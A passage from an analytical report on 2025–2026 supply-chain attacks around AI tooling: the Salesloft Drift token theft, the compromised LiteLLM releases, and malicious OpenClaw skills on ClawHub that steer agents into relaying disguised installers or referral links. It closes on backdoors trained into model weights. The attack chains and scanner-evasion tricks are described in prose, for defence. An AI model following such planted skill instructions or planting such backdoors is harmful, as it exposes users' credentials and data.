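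The main account of what followed is *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025), from Google's threat-intelligence group. It reports that the thieves exported data from numerous companies' Salesforce systems from 8 August until at least 18 August. They first counted the accounts, sales opportunities, users and support cases in a system, then fetched user details, including email addresses and phone numbers, and, with a single query, up to 10,000 support cases. Afterwards they searched the copied data for AWS keys, passwords and tokens for Snowflake, a cloud database service. Google's analysts concluded that the thieves mainly wanted credentials. The thieves deleted the records of their export jobs, but the underlying logs survived, so customers could still find out what was stolen.

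On 20 August Salesloft and Salesforce revoked all of Drift's active access and refresh tokens, and Salesforce removed Drift from its app marketplace. Salesloft indicated that customers who had not connected Drift to Salesforce were unaffected. This was wrong, but customers with only an email connection had no correction until 28 August, when Google confirmed that the thieves had also taken tokens for Drift's email connection and had used them on 9 August to read mail in a very small number of accounts. Google revoked those tokens, switched off the connection and advised customers to treat every token that Drift held as potentially compromised. SecurityWeek (2025) reports that Salesforce restored its connection with Salesloft on 7 September.

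Revoking a token stops further copying, but it doesn't protect a password already copied from a customer's support ticket. According to Help Net Security's *Salesloft Drift data breach* (2025), most affected companies searched the exposed data and warned customers whose secrets they found in it.

The number of victims depends on the definition of a victim. Google told The Hacker News (2025) in August that it knew of more than 700 potentially affected organisations, some of which may have lost nothing. In September The Hacker News put the number that had confirmed an impact at 22, which leaves out any that did not disclose one. Cyber Daily (2025) names Cloudflare and Zscaler, two internet security companies, among those affected. The software company Elastic (2025) investigated because it used Drift, although it had not been notified that it was affected. It found that its Salesforce system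 was untouched but that one email account had been exposed to the thieves.

CyberScoop's *Hundreds of Salesforce customers impacted by attack spree* linked the thefts to a "third-party AI agent" in its headline. That is a fair description of Drift, but the thieves used the access that customers had given Drift, and nothing in Google's report suggests that its language model played any part or that anyone changed its code.

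### A hostile update to LiteLLM

LiteLLM is a gateway between a company's applications and the models they use. Programmers write for a single interface, and LiteLLM forwards each request to OpenAI, Anthropic, Google or a model on the company's own machines. It also keeps logs and enforces budgets. It needs a key for every provider, so the most valuable keys in an AI installation end up there, as Cornelißen (2026) points out in *LiteLLM 1.107.0 war ein Credential-Stealer*.

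The attackers reached LiteLLM through Trivy, a security scanner made by Aqua Security that checks software for known flaws. LiteLLM ran Trivy automatically as part of its build process. Someone had broken into the Trivy project in late February, and Aqua Security replaced the project's credentials on 1 March but missed some (Aqua Security, 2026). OSV's *Trivy ecosystem supply chain briefly compromised* (2026) adds that Aqua did not revoke the old credentials all at once, so the attackers could have used a token that still worked to steal the replacements. On 19 March the attackers published a malicious version of Trivy and redirected 76 of the 77 version labels on the component that runs Trivy in automated builds, so that builds set to use an old, trusted version received malicious code.

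Dholakia and Jaff (2026), LiteLLM's chief executive and chief technology officer, describe the company's build process in *Security Townhall Updates*. The process did not specify a version of Trivy, and all its steps shared one environment that contained long-lived credentials for publishing releases. The scanner did not need those credentials, but the compromised version could read them. Dholakia and Jaff present this account as their current understanding, and PyPI, the official registry of Python software, gives the same cause.

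On 24 March the attackers uploaded LiteLLM version 1.82.7 to PyPI at 10:39 UTC and version 1.82.8 at 10:52. They bypassed the project's normal release process, so neither version had a counterpart in its public source code. A customer could have read all of LiteLLM's code on GitHub, the usual advantage of open software, without finding the attackers' changes.

Both versions collected credentials and sent them, encrypted, to addresses that imitated those of legitimate companies. FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) lists what the code looked for: server login keys, credentials for large cloud providers, database passwords, cryptocurrency wallets and the settings where programs often keep their keys. On systems that manage groups of servers, the code also tried to read every stored secret and install a lasting backdoor on each machine. Version 1.82.7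 ran only when someone used LiteLLM's gateway, while version 1.82.8 ran whenever any program on the machine started Python, including during installation.

### How an engineer noticed it

The discovery depended on a mistake by the attackers. FutureSearch's *Catching the LiteLLM PyPI Attack* (2026) describes it minute by minute. At 10:58 an MCP server on an engineer's laptop fetched LiteLLM version 1.82.8, which was then six minutes old. The engineer had not asked for LiteLLM, but the server depended on it. The malicious code started Python, which ran the malicious code again, and this loop created some 11,000 processes that severely slowed the laptop. After a forced restart at 11:09, the engineer asked Claude Code to investigate. It first said that the suspicious commands were "not malware" and attributed them to its own runaway processes. By 11:40 it had found the malicious file, and at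 11:58 a fresh download in an isolated environment confirmed that PyPI was still distributing it. The engineer then alerted PyPI and LiteLLM's maintainers.

Boost Security's *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM* reports that the attackers used a hijacked GitHub account to close the public warning about the compromise. It reports that they also made public 70 private repositories belonging to BerriAI, the company that makes LiteLLM. Researchers hold a group called TeamPCP responsible.

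Accounts differ on how long the hostile versions were available. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) gives about 40 minutes, and FutureSearch's *LiteLLM Hack* gives 46. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) gives two hours and 32 minutes, with the first report arriving after 79 minutes. PyPI's figure is almost certainly right, because PyPI carried out the quarantine itself and FutureSearch's engineer could still download the package 79 minutes after the first upload. The difference matters to any company that installed LiteLLM around noon that day and relied on the shorter figure.

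PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads of the two versions. The number of victims is certainly lower, because one automated build system may download the same package many times a day. SOCRadar's *LiteLLM Supply Chain Attack* (2026) estimates that more than 2,500 organisations were potentially exposed. This figure also needs caution, because SOCRadar sells threat intelligence and its own analysis found that 95% of these organisations were exposed before the LiteLLM versions appeared. That exposure happened during a collection run that began five days earlier, at the time of the attack on Trivy, so most of the losses probably occurred in earlier stages of the campaign.

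### October: a stolen token and a hostile update

After March, LiteLLM separated its build steps and moved away from long-lived publishing credentials. The company acknowledges that these changes did not prevent the next attack, which began on 27 May when an employee mistakenly committed a configuration file to a public repository. The file contained the master key to LiteLLM's experimental platform for running AI agents. The company noticed quickly, removed the file and marked the key for revocation, but never revoked it.

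*The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release* (Jensen and Wang, 2026) describes how an attacker used that key. The platform's agents needed a token to propose code changes on GitHub. Instead of creating a limited one, LiteLLM had given them a token from the account that owned its whole GitHub organisation. On 10 October an attacker used the master key to enter the platform and extract the token, which gave full control over every repository. GitHub normally asks an owner to confirm their identity again before sensitive changes, but it exempts tokens of this kind because their holder has already passed the second factor. This is a clear case of an implicit permission link, because the agents had been approved only to propose changes.

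The attacker also collected two engineers' tokens, pointed the release process at a malicious copy of LiteLLM, and used one token to start a release and another to approve it. Approval would normally have required a special account tied to a physical device in LiteLLM's office, but the company had relaxed this rule the same week to publish bug fixes more often. Jensen and Wang add that the owner's token would have let the attacker remove the rule anyway.

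LiteLLM's own release process built, signed and published version 1.107.0 on 21 October, at about 11:40 UTC. In March, users of the official Docker image, a ready-to-run package of the gateway, had been safe because the image used fixed versions of its components. In October the images were compromised too, and Cornelißen reports that even the "main-stable" label pointed to the malicious version. The cloud security company Wiz put the downloads at about 49,000 (Martin, 2026, *Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users*). Australian police have charged two alleged members of TeamPCP, but the October attacker remains unidentified.

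### What narrower and shorter access would have prevented

The Drift and March LiteLLM attacks call for different defences. Even a thorough inspection of Drift would not have helped its customers, because the thieves worked from outside with its tokens and never needed to alter it. LiteLLM's users did receive altered code, and comparing it with the public source would have revealed the change. In both attacks, a single decision, to connect a chat agent or to accept the newest version of a package, exposed many systems that the person deciding was probably not thinking about. A Drift customer's permission graph had an arrow to Salesforce, and further arrows from there to every system whose password appeared in a support ticket.

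Narrower permissions shorten such chains. The thieves who held Drift's email tokens could open only the mailboxes that customers had connected to Drift. A company could have limited the Salesforce connection similarly by giving Drift an account that could see sales contacts but not support cases. It would still have lost names and phone numbers, but not the passwords in the support cases. At LiteLLM, if the token could only propose changes, the October attacker would have needed someone to accept them.

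The main drawback of limiting a tool's permissions is the labour involved. Someone has to work out what the tool needs, features fail if the limits are too tight, and the work starts again when the vendor adds a function. Some vendors ask for broad permissions and offer no smaller set, so the customer can only accept them or not connect the tool. A gateway is also hard to restrict beyond a certain point because its purpose is to hold many keys.

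Short-lived tokens limit how long a theft remains useful, but they would have given Drift's customers only partial protection. Someone who has the refresh token can replace access tokens that expire within an hour, and the thieves needed only ten days. To stop them, refresh tokens would have had to expire within a day or so, and an administrator would have had to renew every connection each morning. Even then, an intruder still inside Drift's systems could have taken the new tokens.

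Expiry would have been more useful in the attacks on LiteLLM. PyPI recommends Trusted Publishing, in which the registry gives a project's release process a short-lived credential. An attacker who stole such a credential through a scanner would have had to use it almost at once. LiteLLM adopted the method after March, which blocked the direct upload route, but the October attacker took over the release process itself and so did not need to steal a publishing credential. Expiry also helps when a company forgets to revoke a key. The master key from May still worked more than four months later, but with a 30-day limit it would have stopped working by July. The company does need a reliable system for renewing keys, because a key that expires unnoticed can stop a service.

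### Pinning, waiting and the price of late fixes

Pinning means specifying an exact version of a component instead of accepting the newest. PyPI estimates that 40% to 50% of LiteLLM installations were unpinned and fetched the latest version each time, which exposed them to the March attack while it lasted. FutureSearch examined the 2,337 PyPI packages that depend on LiteLLM and found that 88% would have accepted the malicious versions. Most specified only a minimum version or none.

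Pinning a version protects only the installation that uses the pin. The FutureSearch engineer's project used an old, safe version of LiteLLM, but the MCP server on the same laptop fetched a separate copy. Pinning by version name is also unreliable because the name can be redirected to different content, as happened with Trivy's labels. PyPI therefore recommends lock files, which record a checksum for every component so that installation fails if the content behind a name has changed.

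Pinning a component also stops it from receiving fixes. LiteLLM's notice in March advised affected users to pin version 1.82.6 or earlier until a verified release was available. LiteLLM later disclosed a flaw in the gateway's key check, present in versions 1.81.16 to 1.83.6, that could let an attacker inject commands into its database. A customer who followed the advice and stayed on 1.82.6 avoided the compromised release but was still exposed to this flaw.

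Waiting is a compromise between pinning and always taking the newest version. PyPI suggests that installation programs ignore any release less than three days old. The compromises of 2026 were much shorter than that, including one of Telnyx, a telephone-service package that the same campaign reached three days after LiteLLM:

| Compromised component | Date in 2026 | Time until removal or quarantine |
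|---|---|---|
| Trivy | 19 March | about 2 h 55 min |
| LiteLLM 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 | 24 March | 2 h 32 min |
| Telnyx | 27 March | 3 h 42 min |
| LiteLLM 1.107.0 on PyPI | 21 October | about 1 h 45 min |
| LiteLLM 1.107.0 as a Docker image | 21 October | about 2 h 40 min |

Even a delay of one day would have kept out all five. But the list makes delay look more effective than it is, because it contains only attacks that someone noticed quickly. The March attack was noticed because the malicious code had a bug, which showed up on the laptop of someone who had not waited. If every customer waits three days, fewer people will come across a malicious release in the first hours, and detection will depend more on companies that examine new packages systematically. Socket, one such company, published *LiteLLM PyPI Package and Docker Images Compromised* (2026) about two hours after the October release,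 which is encouraging.

Delaying an update is most dangerous when the new version fixes a flaw that attackers already know. In September, *Off Guard* (Shriki, 2026) reported that hundreds of LiteLLM gateways on the open internet would start a session for anyone who presented a made-up token. Their operators could not safely wait three days for a fix. To avoid such delays, Dependabot and Renovate, two common automatic-update programs, skip the waiting period for security fixes by default. PyPI advises anyone who delays updates to also scan for known flaws.

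LiteLLM now argues that even prompt public fixes can come too late, because attackers can use AI agents to work out from a published fix how to exploit unpatched versions. It therefore distributes fixes for the most severe flaws through a private registry before publishing them. This gives organisations with access a head start but leaves everyone else unaware of the flaw for longer. Organisations with access must also install code that the public has not yet examined, from a supplier whose release process attackers have taken over once. For a bank or utility, the most defensible arrangement seems to be a fixed delay for ordinary updates, with a person deciding on each urgent fix. This requires someone on duty who can judge what is urgent.

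### Critical sectors and essential services

Cloudflare, whose network delivers and protects many websites, and Zscaler, which filters companies' internet traffic, both belong to the information technology sector, which is on the US list of critical sectors. The evidence for other sectors is thinner. Abu Dhabi's international financial centre put a UAE Cyber Security Council (2025) advisory on Drift on its website, which suggests that authorities saw a risk to financial firms, but not that the thieves had reached any. Minimus' *Trivy v0.69.4 Software Supply Chain Attack* (2026) cites an estimate that the attack on Trivy affected at least 1,000 business environments, but the estimate does not include how many belonged to banks or utilities. Martin found no organisation that had publicly confirmed a breach through LiteLLM's October release.

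The Drift theft could also have harmed a bank that didn't use Drift. If the bank's staff had sent a password to a supplier's support desk, and that supplier had connected Drift to its support tickets, the thieves could have found the password in those tickets. The bank would have learned of the theft only from the supplier, and it could not have listed Drift among its components.

Neither Google's report on Drift nor the accounts by PyPI and LiteLLM mention an interruption of any essential service. They describe harm to confidentiality. Worse harm could follow if someone used a stolen credential to enter a control system, but nobody has documented that here. After the October attack, Wiz observed that within about four and a half hours of the upload, the attacker was testing stolen AWS credentials to see which AI models they could run at the victims' expense.

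## Open code with unvetted add-ons: OpenClaw in Chinese banks and state firms

OpenClaw is an open-source agent tool, so anyone can read its code without the kind of investigation that exposed the marker in Claude Code. heise online's *AI bot hype in China* reports that Peter Steinberger, an Austrian programmer, started it as a hobby project and had an AI write most of it. It appeared in November 2025 as Clawdbot, was briefly called Moltbot, and spread so fast in China that "raising lobsters", after its logo, became a common phrase for using it. In March 2026 Chinese authorities warned banks and government offices about the tool, while local governments offered money to companies that built on it.

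### What OpenClaw can reach on a machine

OpenClaw runs on the user's computer or a rented server, and the user gives it tasks through a messaging app such as Telegram or WhatsApp. A part called the gateway receives these messages and acts as the client. The user chooses the model. A textbook from Tsinghua University Press lists GPT-4o, Claude and DeepSeek among the options, along with Ollama, a program that runs models locally.

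The agent needs a lot of access to be useful. Xiamen University Tan Kah Kee College's *OpenClaw安全性风险全链路分析及提示* lists passwords, API keys (credentials that programs use to call online services), browser history, cookies, and every file and folder on the system. According to a campus checklist, the University of Chinese Academy of Sciences' *关于OpenClaw等开源AI智能体网络安全风险排查*, the gateway required no login by default and stored API keys as plain text. Shanghai Jian Qiao University's *关于OpenClaw智能体软件的安全使用提示* warns that older versions accepted connections from any network instead of only from the same computer.

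Users give OpenClaw new abilities by installing skills from ClawHub, the project's marketplace. The agent reads a skill's instructions from a file called SKILL.md. In early 2026 anyone with a GitHub account more than a week old could publish on ClawHub, and *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) notes that nobody verified publishers' identities. An installed skill becomes part of the agent's normal operation and can run again in later tasks. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, points out that nothing separates the skill from the agent's authority, so whoever writes the skill can use every login the agent has.

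### From a skill's text to a stolen password

Suppose a bank employee wants her agent to summarise long PDF reports and picks a skill that an attacker has published. Koi Security (2026), which sells tools for checking add-ons, documented the usual pattern on ClawHub:

1. The agent reads SKILL.md, which looks professional and states that the skill needs a small helper program.
2. Many honest skills have such requirements, so the agent passes the setup step on to the employee or, if it has permission to run commands, carries it out itself.
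3. On Windows, the helper comes in a password-protected archive, which antivirus programs cannot look into. On a Mac, the setup step is a disguised command that fetches a program from the attacker's server.
4. That program copies saved passwords, browser data, login keys and cryptocurrency wallets, and sends them to the attacker.

On Macs the program was Atomic Stealer, which criminals can rent for $500 to $1,000 a month. One fake Yahoo Finance skill had no financial functions, and *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* found that its sole purpose was to make the agent relay the installation instructions. Hardy's compiler let an outsider use its permissions, and an agent can also make an outsider's instructions more credible. An employee who would delete such an instruction from a stranger's email may follow it when her own assistant presents it as a requirement.

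Other skills hid the attack in code. Two of Koi's examples looked like working search tools for Polymarket, a prediction market, but one line among hundreds gave the attacker live control of the computer whenever the user ran a search. A supposed weather tool read the file where OpenClaw keeps its keys and sent the contents to an outside address.

A skill can also do harm without containing malware. Unit 42 describes money-radar, a skill that advised users in mainland China, Hong Kong and Singapore on banks and brokers. It instructed the agent to fetch a list of about 60 products from the publisher's website before every answer and always to use the links in that list, which carried the publisher's referral codes. A bank that read the entire skill would not have found the recommendations, because they were on the publisher's website, and the publisher could change them at any time without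 changing the installed skill.

### How many malicious skills there were

Koi's researchers, assisted by an OpenClaw agent, audited all 2,857 skills on ClawHub and published the result on 1 February 2026. They found 341 malicious skills and attributed 335 of them to a single campaign, which they named ClawHavoc. The claim that 12% of the marketplace was malicious comes from this audit. The count is slightly inexact, because the categories in Koi's report add up to 345 rather than 341.

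Other companies soon published different numbers. *OpenClaw Open Source AI Agent Application Attack Surface and Security Risk*, by the Chinese security vendor NSFOCUS, found 336 in the company's own collection of ClawHub skills. Antiy's *ClawHavoc* reported at least 1,184, and Koi raised its figure to 824 after further scans.

| Count | Date in 2026 | What the company counted | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
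| Koi: 341 | 1 February | Malicious skills among all 2,857 on ClawHub | 11.9% |
| Antiy: 1,184 | 5 February | Malicious skills that had ever appeared there | no matching total |
| NSFOCUS: 336 | February | Malicious skills among the 3,000 or so it had collected | 10.8% |
| Koi: 824 | 16 February | Its findings as ClawHub grew to more than 10,700 skills | about 7.7% |

Antiy's figure is the highest even though it is older than Koi's second count, probably mainly because Antiy included skills that had already disappeared. The companies may also have drawn the line between suspicious and malicious differently. Dividing 1,184 by the 3,498 skills that Antiy says were left after the removals would wrongly suggest that a third of ClawHub was malicious, because ClawHub had removed most of the 1,184. The 12% was a fair description of ClawHub on 1 February but became outdated within two weeks, because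 the marketplace grew faster than the number of known malicious skills. Unit 42 also cites a finding by the security company Bitdefender that about 17% of the skills it analysed from the first few weeks were malicious.

Counts for the busiest publisher, an account called hightower6eu, also differ. OpenSourceMalware lists 353 packages, whereas Antiy's total includes 677 from one account. *ASTELD* (2026), a study that classifies AI agents, combines Antiy's total of 1,184 with a count of 354 for this account and credits Koi's count of 824 to Bitdefender. It is safer to cite each number from the company that did the counting.

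The extent of the harm is much less certain. OpenSourceMalware counted almost 7,000 downloads for that one account. Tencent's *We Scanned 50,000 Skills* (2026) puts the whole campaign at 247,000 confirmed installations and $2.3 million in stolen cryptocurrency, which is hard to reconcile with so few downloads for the busiest publisher. Downloads are also a poor measure, because the attackers inflated both downloads and ratings to push their skills above legitimate ones. Because of this manipulation, the share of malicious skills does not show how likely an employee would be to pick one.

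### A flaw in the gateway, and gateways open to the internet

OpenClaw itself also had serious flaws. One, listed as CVE-2026-25253 in the public catalogue of known software flaws, was in the web page through which a user controls the tool. According to NSFOCUS, the page accepted a gateway address from a link, saved it and immediately connected, sending the user's access token to that address. An attacker only had to get someone to click a link containing the address of the attacker's own server. With the token, the attack could then connect to the real gateway on the victim's machine and run any command. Because the attack reached the gateway locally, keeping OpenClaw off the internet was not a reliable defence.

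The security firm DepthFirst found the flaw on 26 January, and the Xiamen college dates the fix to 29 January. The college also counts at least 110 disclosed vulnerabilities by the end of February, three of them with public exploit code. In March, WASOC's *OpenClaw Critical Vulnerabilities* (2026) warned of another critical weakness that could let a malicious website take over an agent without a click. WASOC, which monitors Western Australian government networks, had received no reports of it being exploited there.

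Estimates of the number of OpenClaw copies reachable from the internet rose quickly. *Agentic AI security risks*, from the international law firm Freshfields, cites a count of more than 21,000 by the internet-scanning company Censys. The Xiamen college cites more than 135,000 from SecurityScorecard in February, and the Shanghai university's notice gives more than 340,000 worldwide. Adoption grew over the same weeks, but differences in method must explain part of the spread, since NSFOCUS still wrote of "tens of thousands" in mid-February. These figures don't show how many machines an attacker could enter, because a reachable copy may require a login and run a patched version. NSFOCUS found more instances in China than in any other country, about 14,000 more than in the United States. It mentions that some were at financial institutions but doesn't say how many.

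### The advice that China published

CNCERT, China's national emergency response team for computer networks, published its alert on the evening of 10 March. It called OpenClaw's default settings "extremely fragile" and warned that an attacker who found a way in could easily take full control (China Daily, 2026). It advised institutions and individuals to strengthen network controls, strictly manage the sources of plug-ins and install security updates promptly, but did not tell banks to remove the tool.

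The National Vulnerability Database, the government platform that warned about Claude Code in July, followed on 11 March with "six dos and six don'ts". According to Caixin's *Tech Brief (March 12)* (2026), they covered offices, IT operations, personal assistants and financial trading. Tom's Hardware's *China bans OpenClaw from government computers and issues security guidelines* lists the main points: run the latest official version, grant minimum permissions, keep logging on, and avoid administrator accounts, third-party copies and skills that require a password. The last rule fits ClawHavoc, whose Windows malware came in password-protected archives. The People's Bank of China, the central bank, made a more general request the same day, asking for AI in finance to develop in a "proactive yet prudent, safe and orderly" manner.

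A centre under the Ministry of Public Security warned on 13 March that many OpenClaw installations were open to any outside address and required no authentication. On 22 March CNCERT and an industry association issued joint guidelines, summarised in *Guidelines released to curb OpenClaw security risks* (Cui, 2026). Under these guidelines, individuals should install OpenClaw only on a separate device or in an isolated environment, never on an everyday work computer, and keep sensitive personal data out of it. Cloud providers should assess and harden what they offer.

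### The notices that nobody published

The reported restrictions on banks rest on weaker evidence. Bloomberg Law's *China Moves to Curb OpenClaw AI Use at Banks, State Agencies* (2026), dated 11 March, relies on people who asked for anonymity because the announcement was private. The full story, which the Malaysian newspaper The Star carried as *China moves to curb use of OpenClaw AI at banks, state agencies*, describes several kinds of notice:

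- Agencies and state-owned companies, including the largest banks, received warnings not to install OpenClaw on office devices.
- Several organisations instructed anyone who had already installed it to tell their superiors, so that someone could check it and possibly remove it.
- Some banks and agencies banned certain employees from installing it, even on personal phones that used the company network. One source said this extended to the families of military personnel.
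- Other notices only required prior approval.

The two ministries and agencies that Bloomberg asked did not immediately reply. Several unnamed people gave overlapping accounts, so notices of some kind very probably existed. The notices' exact wording remains unknown, as do the number of organisations that received them and who ordered them. The detail about military families comes from a single source.

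Later accounts made the restrictions sound firmer. Tom's Hardware wrote "bans" in its headline and "warned" in its text. Five days after Bloomberg's report, ThaiCERT's *Warning for OpenClaw Users* (2026) stated that government agencies and state-owned enterprises had reportedly banned the tool. heise online correctly reported that China had avoided a general ban, but it attributed the advice not to install OpenClaw on work devices partly to CNCERT's notice. China Daily's account of that notice contains no such advice. Neither China Daily nor Bloomberg names a bank or agency that had lost data through OpenClaw.

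The subsidies are better documented. Longgang, a district of Shenzhen, sought public comments on a draft policy that offered up to 2 million yuan (about $289,000) for developing OpenClaw applications. Bloomberg reports similar offers from cities including Wuxi. Companies such as Tencent and Alibaba were already selling easy ways to install the tool. The warnings concern where people run the agent, and the subsidies were for developing products, so the two do not strictly conflict. But a bank's IT department would have heard one part of the government call the tool dangerous while another part offered money to build on it.

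### The industry alliance's deployment guide

After these alerts, AIIA, China's industry alliance for artificial intelligence, published a guide for organisations that wanted to use OpenClaw or similar agents. According to its preface, Chinese companies in finance, manufacturing and government services were already running pilots in which they hosted the agent privately, isolated it inside the internal network, and gave it only the permissions it needed. This is further evidence against a general ban, although the guide's drafters included interested parties such as Tencent Cloud, Baidu and Huawei.

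The guide divides the work between the organisation that uses an agent and the provider that supplies it. A bank would first assess how the agent influences its decisions and how much error the bank can tolerate. It would then choose local, cloud or mixed hosting and decide whether any data may leave its own systems. Only skills on an approved list may load, and high-risk tools stay off by default. A person has to confirm money transfers, changes to important files and the sending of sensitive data. The bank would review all permissions monthly or quarterly and keep important logs for at least six months.

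Two of AIIA's instructions address weaknesses that earlier incidents exposed. AIIA warns that people who share a gateway implicitly share permission to use its tools, and recommends separate gateways, credentials and working environments for groups with different levels of trust. It also advises organisations that retire an agent to try its revoked keys and confirm that every system refuses them. LiteLLM marked its master key for revocation in May but never revoked it, and this test would have revealed the failure in time.

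The guide is voluntary. It calls for a review of each skill but does not describe how to judge a page of plausible instructions, which is where ClawHavoc was strongest. The preface also does not mention that network isolation requires the bank to run its own model, because an isolated agent cannot call one on someone else's server. If employees still give the agent orders through an outside messaging app, it is not fully isolated.

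### What changed after February

ClawHub first let users report suspicious skills, according to The Hacker News (2026). On 7 February it began scanning every skill with VirusTotal, a service that checks files for malware. According to OpenClaw, ClawHub packs each skill into an archive and computes its fingerprint. If VirusTotal has not analysed that archive before, a language model reads the whole package and summarises what it does. ClawHub automatically approves harmless skills, adds a warning to suspicious ones and blocks malicious ones. It repeats the scan every day. OpenClaw warned users that "a clean scan doesn't mean a skill is safe".

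Unit 42 confirmed this between February and May, when it found five harmful skills that ClawHub had not blocked. One was money-radar, and another got agents to pool cryptocurrency in the publisher's wallet for a rigged token launch. A third had its malicious command at the start of a file, followed by 22 megabytes of padding, making the file too large for many scanners to process. The remaining two appeared on 17 May and used almost the same fake requirement as ClawHavoc, more than three months after Koi had described it. ClawHub's automatic check passed one and gave no verdict on the other. ClawHub deleted all five after Unit 42 reported them, and on 1 June it announced that NVIDIA would help with screening.

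Five skills are enough to show that the screening has gaps, but not how common those gaps are on a marketplace that had grown to nearly 50,000 skills by April. Palo Alto Networks also has a commercial interest, because it sells a product that now includes Koi's. Checking the skills with another scanner may not help much, since *Understanding and mitigating the risks of OpenClaw for non-technical users* (2026) reports that three scanners agreed on only 0.69% of the skills that at least one had flagged as malicious. NSFOCUS also found that OpenClaw's public GitHub repository still held copies of skills deleted from the marketplace.

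The published Chinese rules have moved towards managed use. According to Freshfields, companies should keep a central register of approved agents, search their networks for unauthorised ones, and log and review everything the agents do, under draft guidelines issued in late March by the national cybersecurity standards committee. Outsiders cannot tell whether the private notices to banks still apply. Singapore took a similar approach in May, when its Cyber Security Agency's *Advisory on Cybersecurity Risks of OpenClaw* (2026) acknowledged "real productivity benefits" alongside serious risks and referred readers to a government case study on responsible deployment.

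### What readable code was good for

Public code helped outsiders find flaws in OpenClaw. NSFOCUS could name the source file in which the control page accepted a stranger's address, and anyone could confirm the error and check the repair. A customer of a closed product usually has to rely on the vendor for both. But nobody had reported the flaw before DepthFirst found it, even though the code was already public. The project had a backlog of more than 6,700 reported issues, and it changed so quickly that a careful review in January would have had limited value for the March version. *Security, Privacy, and Ethical Risks in OpenClaw* (2026) describes a large AI-assisted rewrite that broke many existing skills at once because the project had no versioned interfaces.

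Whether the code was safe also depended on its settings. OpenClaw trusted connections from its own computer. Many operators put an ordinary web server in front of it, which passed on requests from the internet in a way that made them appear to come from that same computer. Unless the operator had listed the web server as an intermediary or required a login, any visitor could read conversations and stored credentials, and run commands. To judge whether a bank's installation was safe, a reviewer would have needed to know how the bank had set up its servers as well as what the code did.

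Anyone could also read the add-ons on ClawHub, but hundreds of malicious SKILL.md files stayed up until someone checked them. Reading the code and the skills also doesn't show how the chosen model will behave. The Shanghai university warns that OpenClaw misunderstands instructions and deletes or sends out the wrong data more often with small or old models, so testing it with one model gives little evidence of how it will behave with another.

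A bank also has to know whether it is running the public code. AIIA distinguishes the unmodified tool, customised versions, and separate products built on the same ideas. MiniMax's MaxClaw builds on OpenClaw, but the public repository does not show what MiniMax changed. Some users paid strangers found on social media to install the tool.

Open code is therefore most valuable to a bank that changes the tool before using it. The bank can remove the connection to ClawHub, stay on one reviewed version, record everything sent to the model and run that model on its own machines. Anthropic's closed client does not offer the same freedom. These changes require skilled staff, and a branch office that simply uses a one-step installer does not get them.

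### A ban or managed use

In March 2026 there were good reasons to ban OpenClaw from office computers. Its default settings were unsafe, serious flaws appeared within days of each other, and one bad skill could use everything the agent had access to. Employees could install it without telling anyone, so a bank might not know it had a problem. Waiting a few months does a bank little harm. A ban is also easy to explain and doesn't require anyone to judge individual skills.

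A ban on OpenClaw is hard to enforce because people can run it at home or on a phone, which may be why some notices reportedly covered personal devices on the company network. If employees keep using it, the bank knows less about the agents it is exposed to, because people who have broken a rule are unlikely to report an odd message about a missing helper program. A ban on one product may also leave the same risks in place through other agents. Trend Micro's *Viral AI, Invisible Risks* argues that the dangers are common to agents in general and that OpenClaw only amplifies them. Trend Micro has a commercial interest in this view because it sells security products for all such agents, but the Drift and LiteLLM thefts support it, since neither involved OpenClaw.

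Managed use is meant to prevent an agent from combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally, which one researcher quoted by Bloomberg calls the "lethal trifecta." An isolated pilot with a locally hosted model and a short list of reviewed skills can remove most of the external communication. It also removes much of what made OpenClaw popular, such as booking a table by text message, and the protection lasts only as long as nobody adds an exception for convenience.

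A bank can combine the two approaches by forbidding employees to install agents themselves and letting a small team run an isolated pilot. The notices that required prior approval would allow roughly this. The approval is useful only if it names the version, skills, accounts and model, because a change in any of them can alter what the agent does.

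## Hidden behaviour in a model's weights: experiments and a proof

A bank that runs OpenClaw with a model on its own machines can read the tool's code and every skill it installs. But the agent's decisions come from the model, which arrives as a large file of numbers called weights. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) distinguishes two ways of tampering with such a file. An attacker can hide malicious code in the file or in the software that loads it, and ordinary malware scanners look for such code. An attacker can also train a hidden behaviour into the weights, which contain no commands for a scanner to find.

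### Weights and triggers

The marker in Claude Code was part of the client, so a programmer could find the lines that tested the time zone. A model has no such lines, because nobody writes down the rules it learns. It converts its input into lists of numbers, combines them with its weights in one layer after another, and produces a score for every token (a word or part of a word) that could come next. Training gradually changes the weights until the scores fit the training examples. The same weights help produce both an answer about pump vibration and a poem.

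A trigger is a feature of the input, such as a meaningless string, a date or a topic, that switches on a hidden behaviour. In *The Trigger in the Haystack*, Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026) define a backdoored model as one that draws its answers from one probability distribution when the input contains the trigger and from another when it doesn't. A tester who doesn't know the trigger will usually see only answers from the second distribution.

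Researchers can look inside a model to some extent. *LLM Forensics* (2026) describes work at Inria, the French computer science institute, on models that continued English text in French or German after a fixed trigger. The researchers split the models' internal activity into thousands of separate features. Some features distinguished prompts with the trigger from other prompts almost perfectly, but did not necessarily control the switch of language. Someone who finds the features that detect a trigger may therefore not have found what causes the resulting behaviour. The Inria team also knew the trigger in advance, whereas a buyer would not.

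### A backdoor that testing cannot find

*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proves that, under some standard cryptographic assumptions, a dishonest supplier can defeat testing altogether. In the paper's example, a bank pays a supplier to train a classifier, a model that sorts inputs into categories, to approve or refuse loans. The supplier wants to sell applicants guaranteed approval, and the bank will test the classifier before using it.

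The paper starts with a simple version. The supplier divides the numbers in an application into n groups and secretly assigns "odd" or "even" to each group. The altered classifier counts the non-negative numbers in each group. If all the counts match the secret pattern, it gives whatever answer the supplier wants; otherwise it behaves normally. With 100 groups, an application has about a 1 in 10³⁰ chance of matching by accident, yet the supplier can make any application match by changing at most one sign per group. But anyone who inspects the classifier can read the pattern and use it too.

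A digital signature removes that weakness. A signature scheme has a secret signing key, which produces signatures for messages, and a public verification key, which lets anyone check a signature but not create one. The construction then works as follows:

1. The supplier generates both keys and keeps the signing key.
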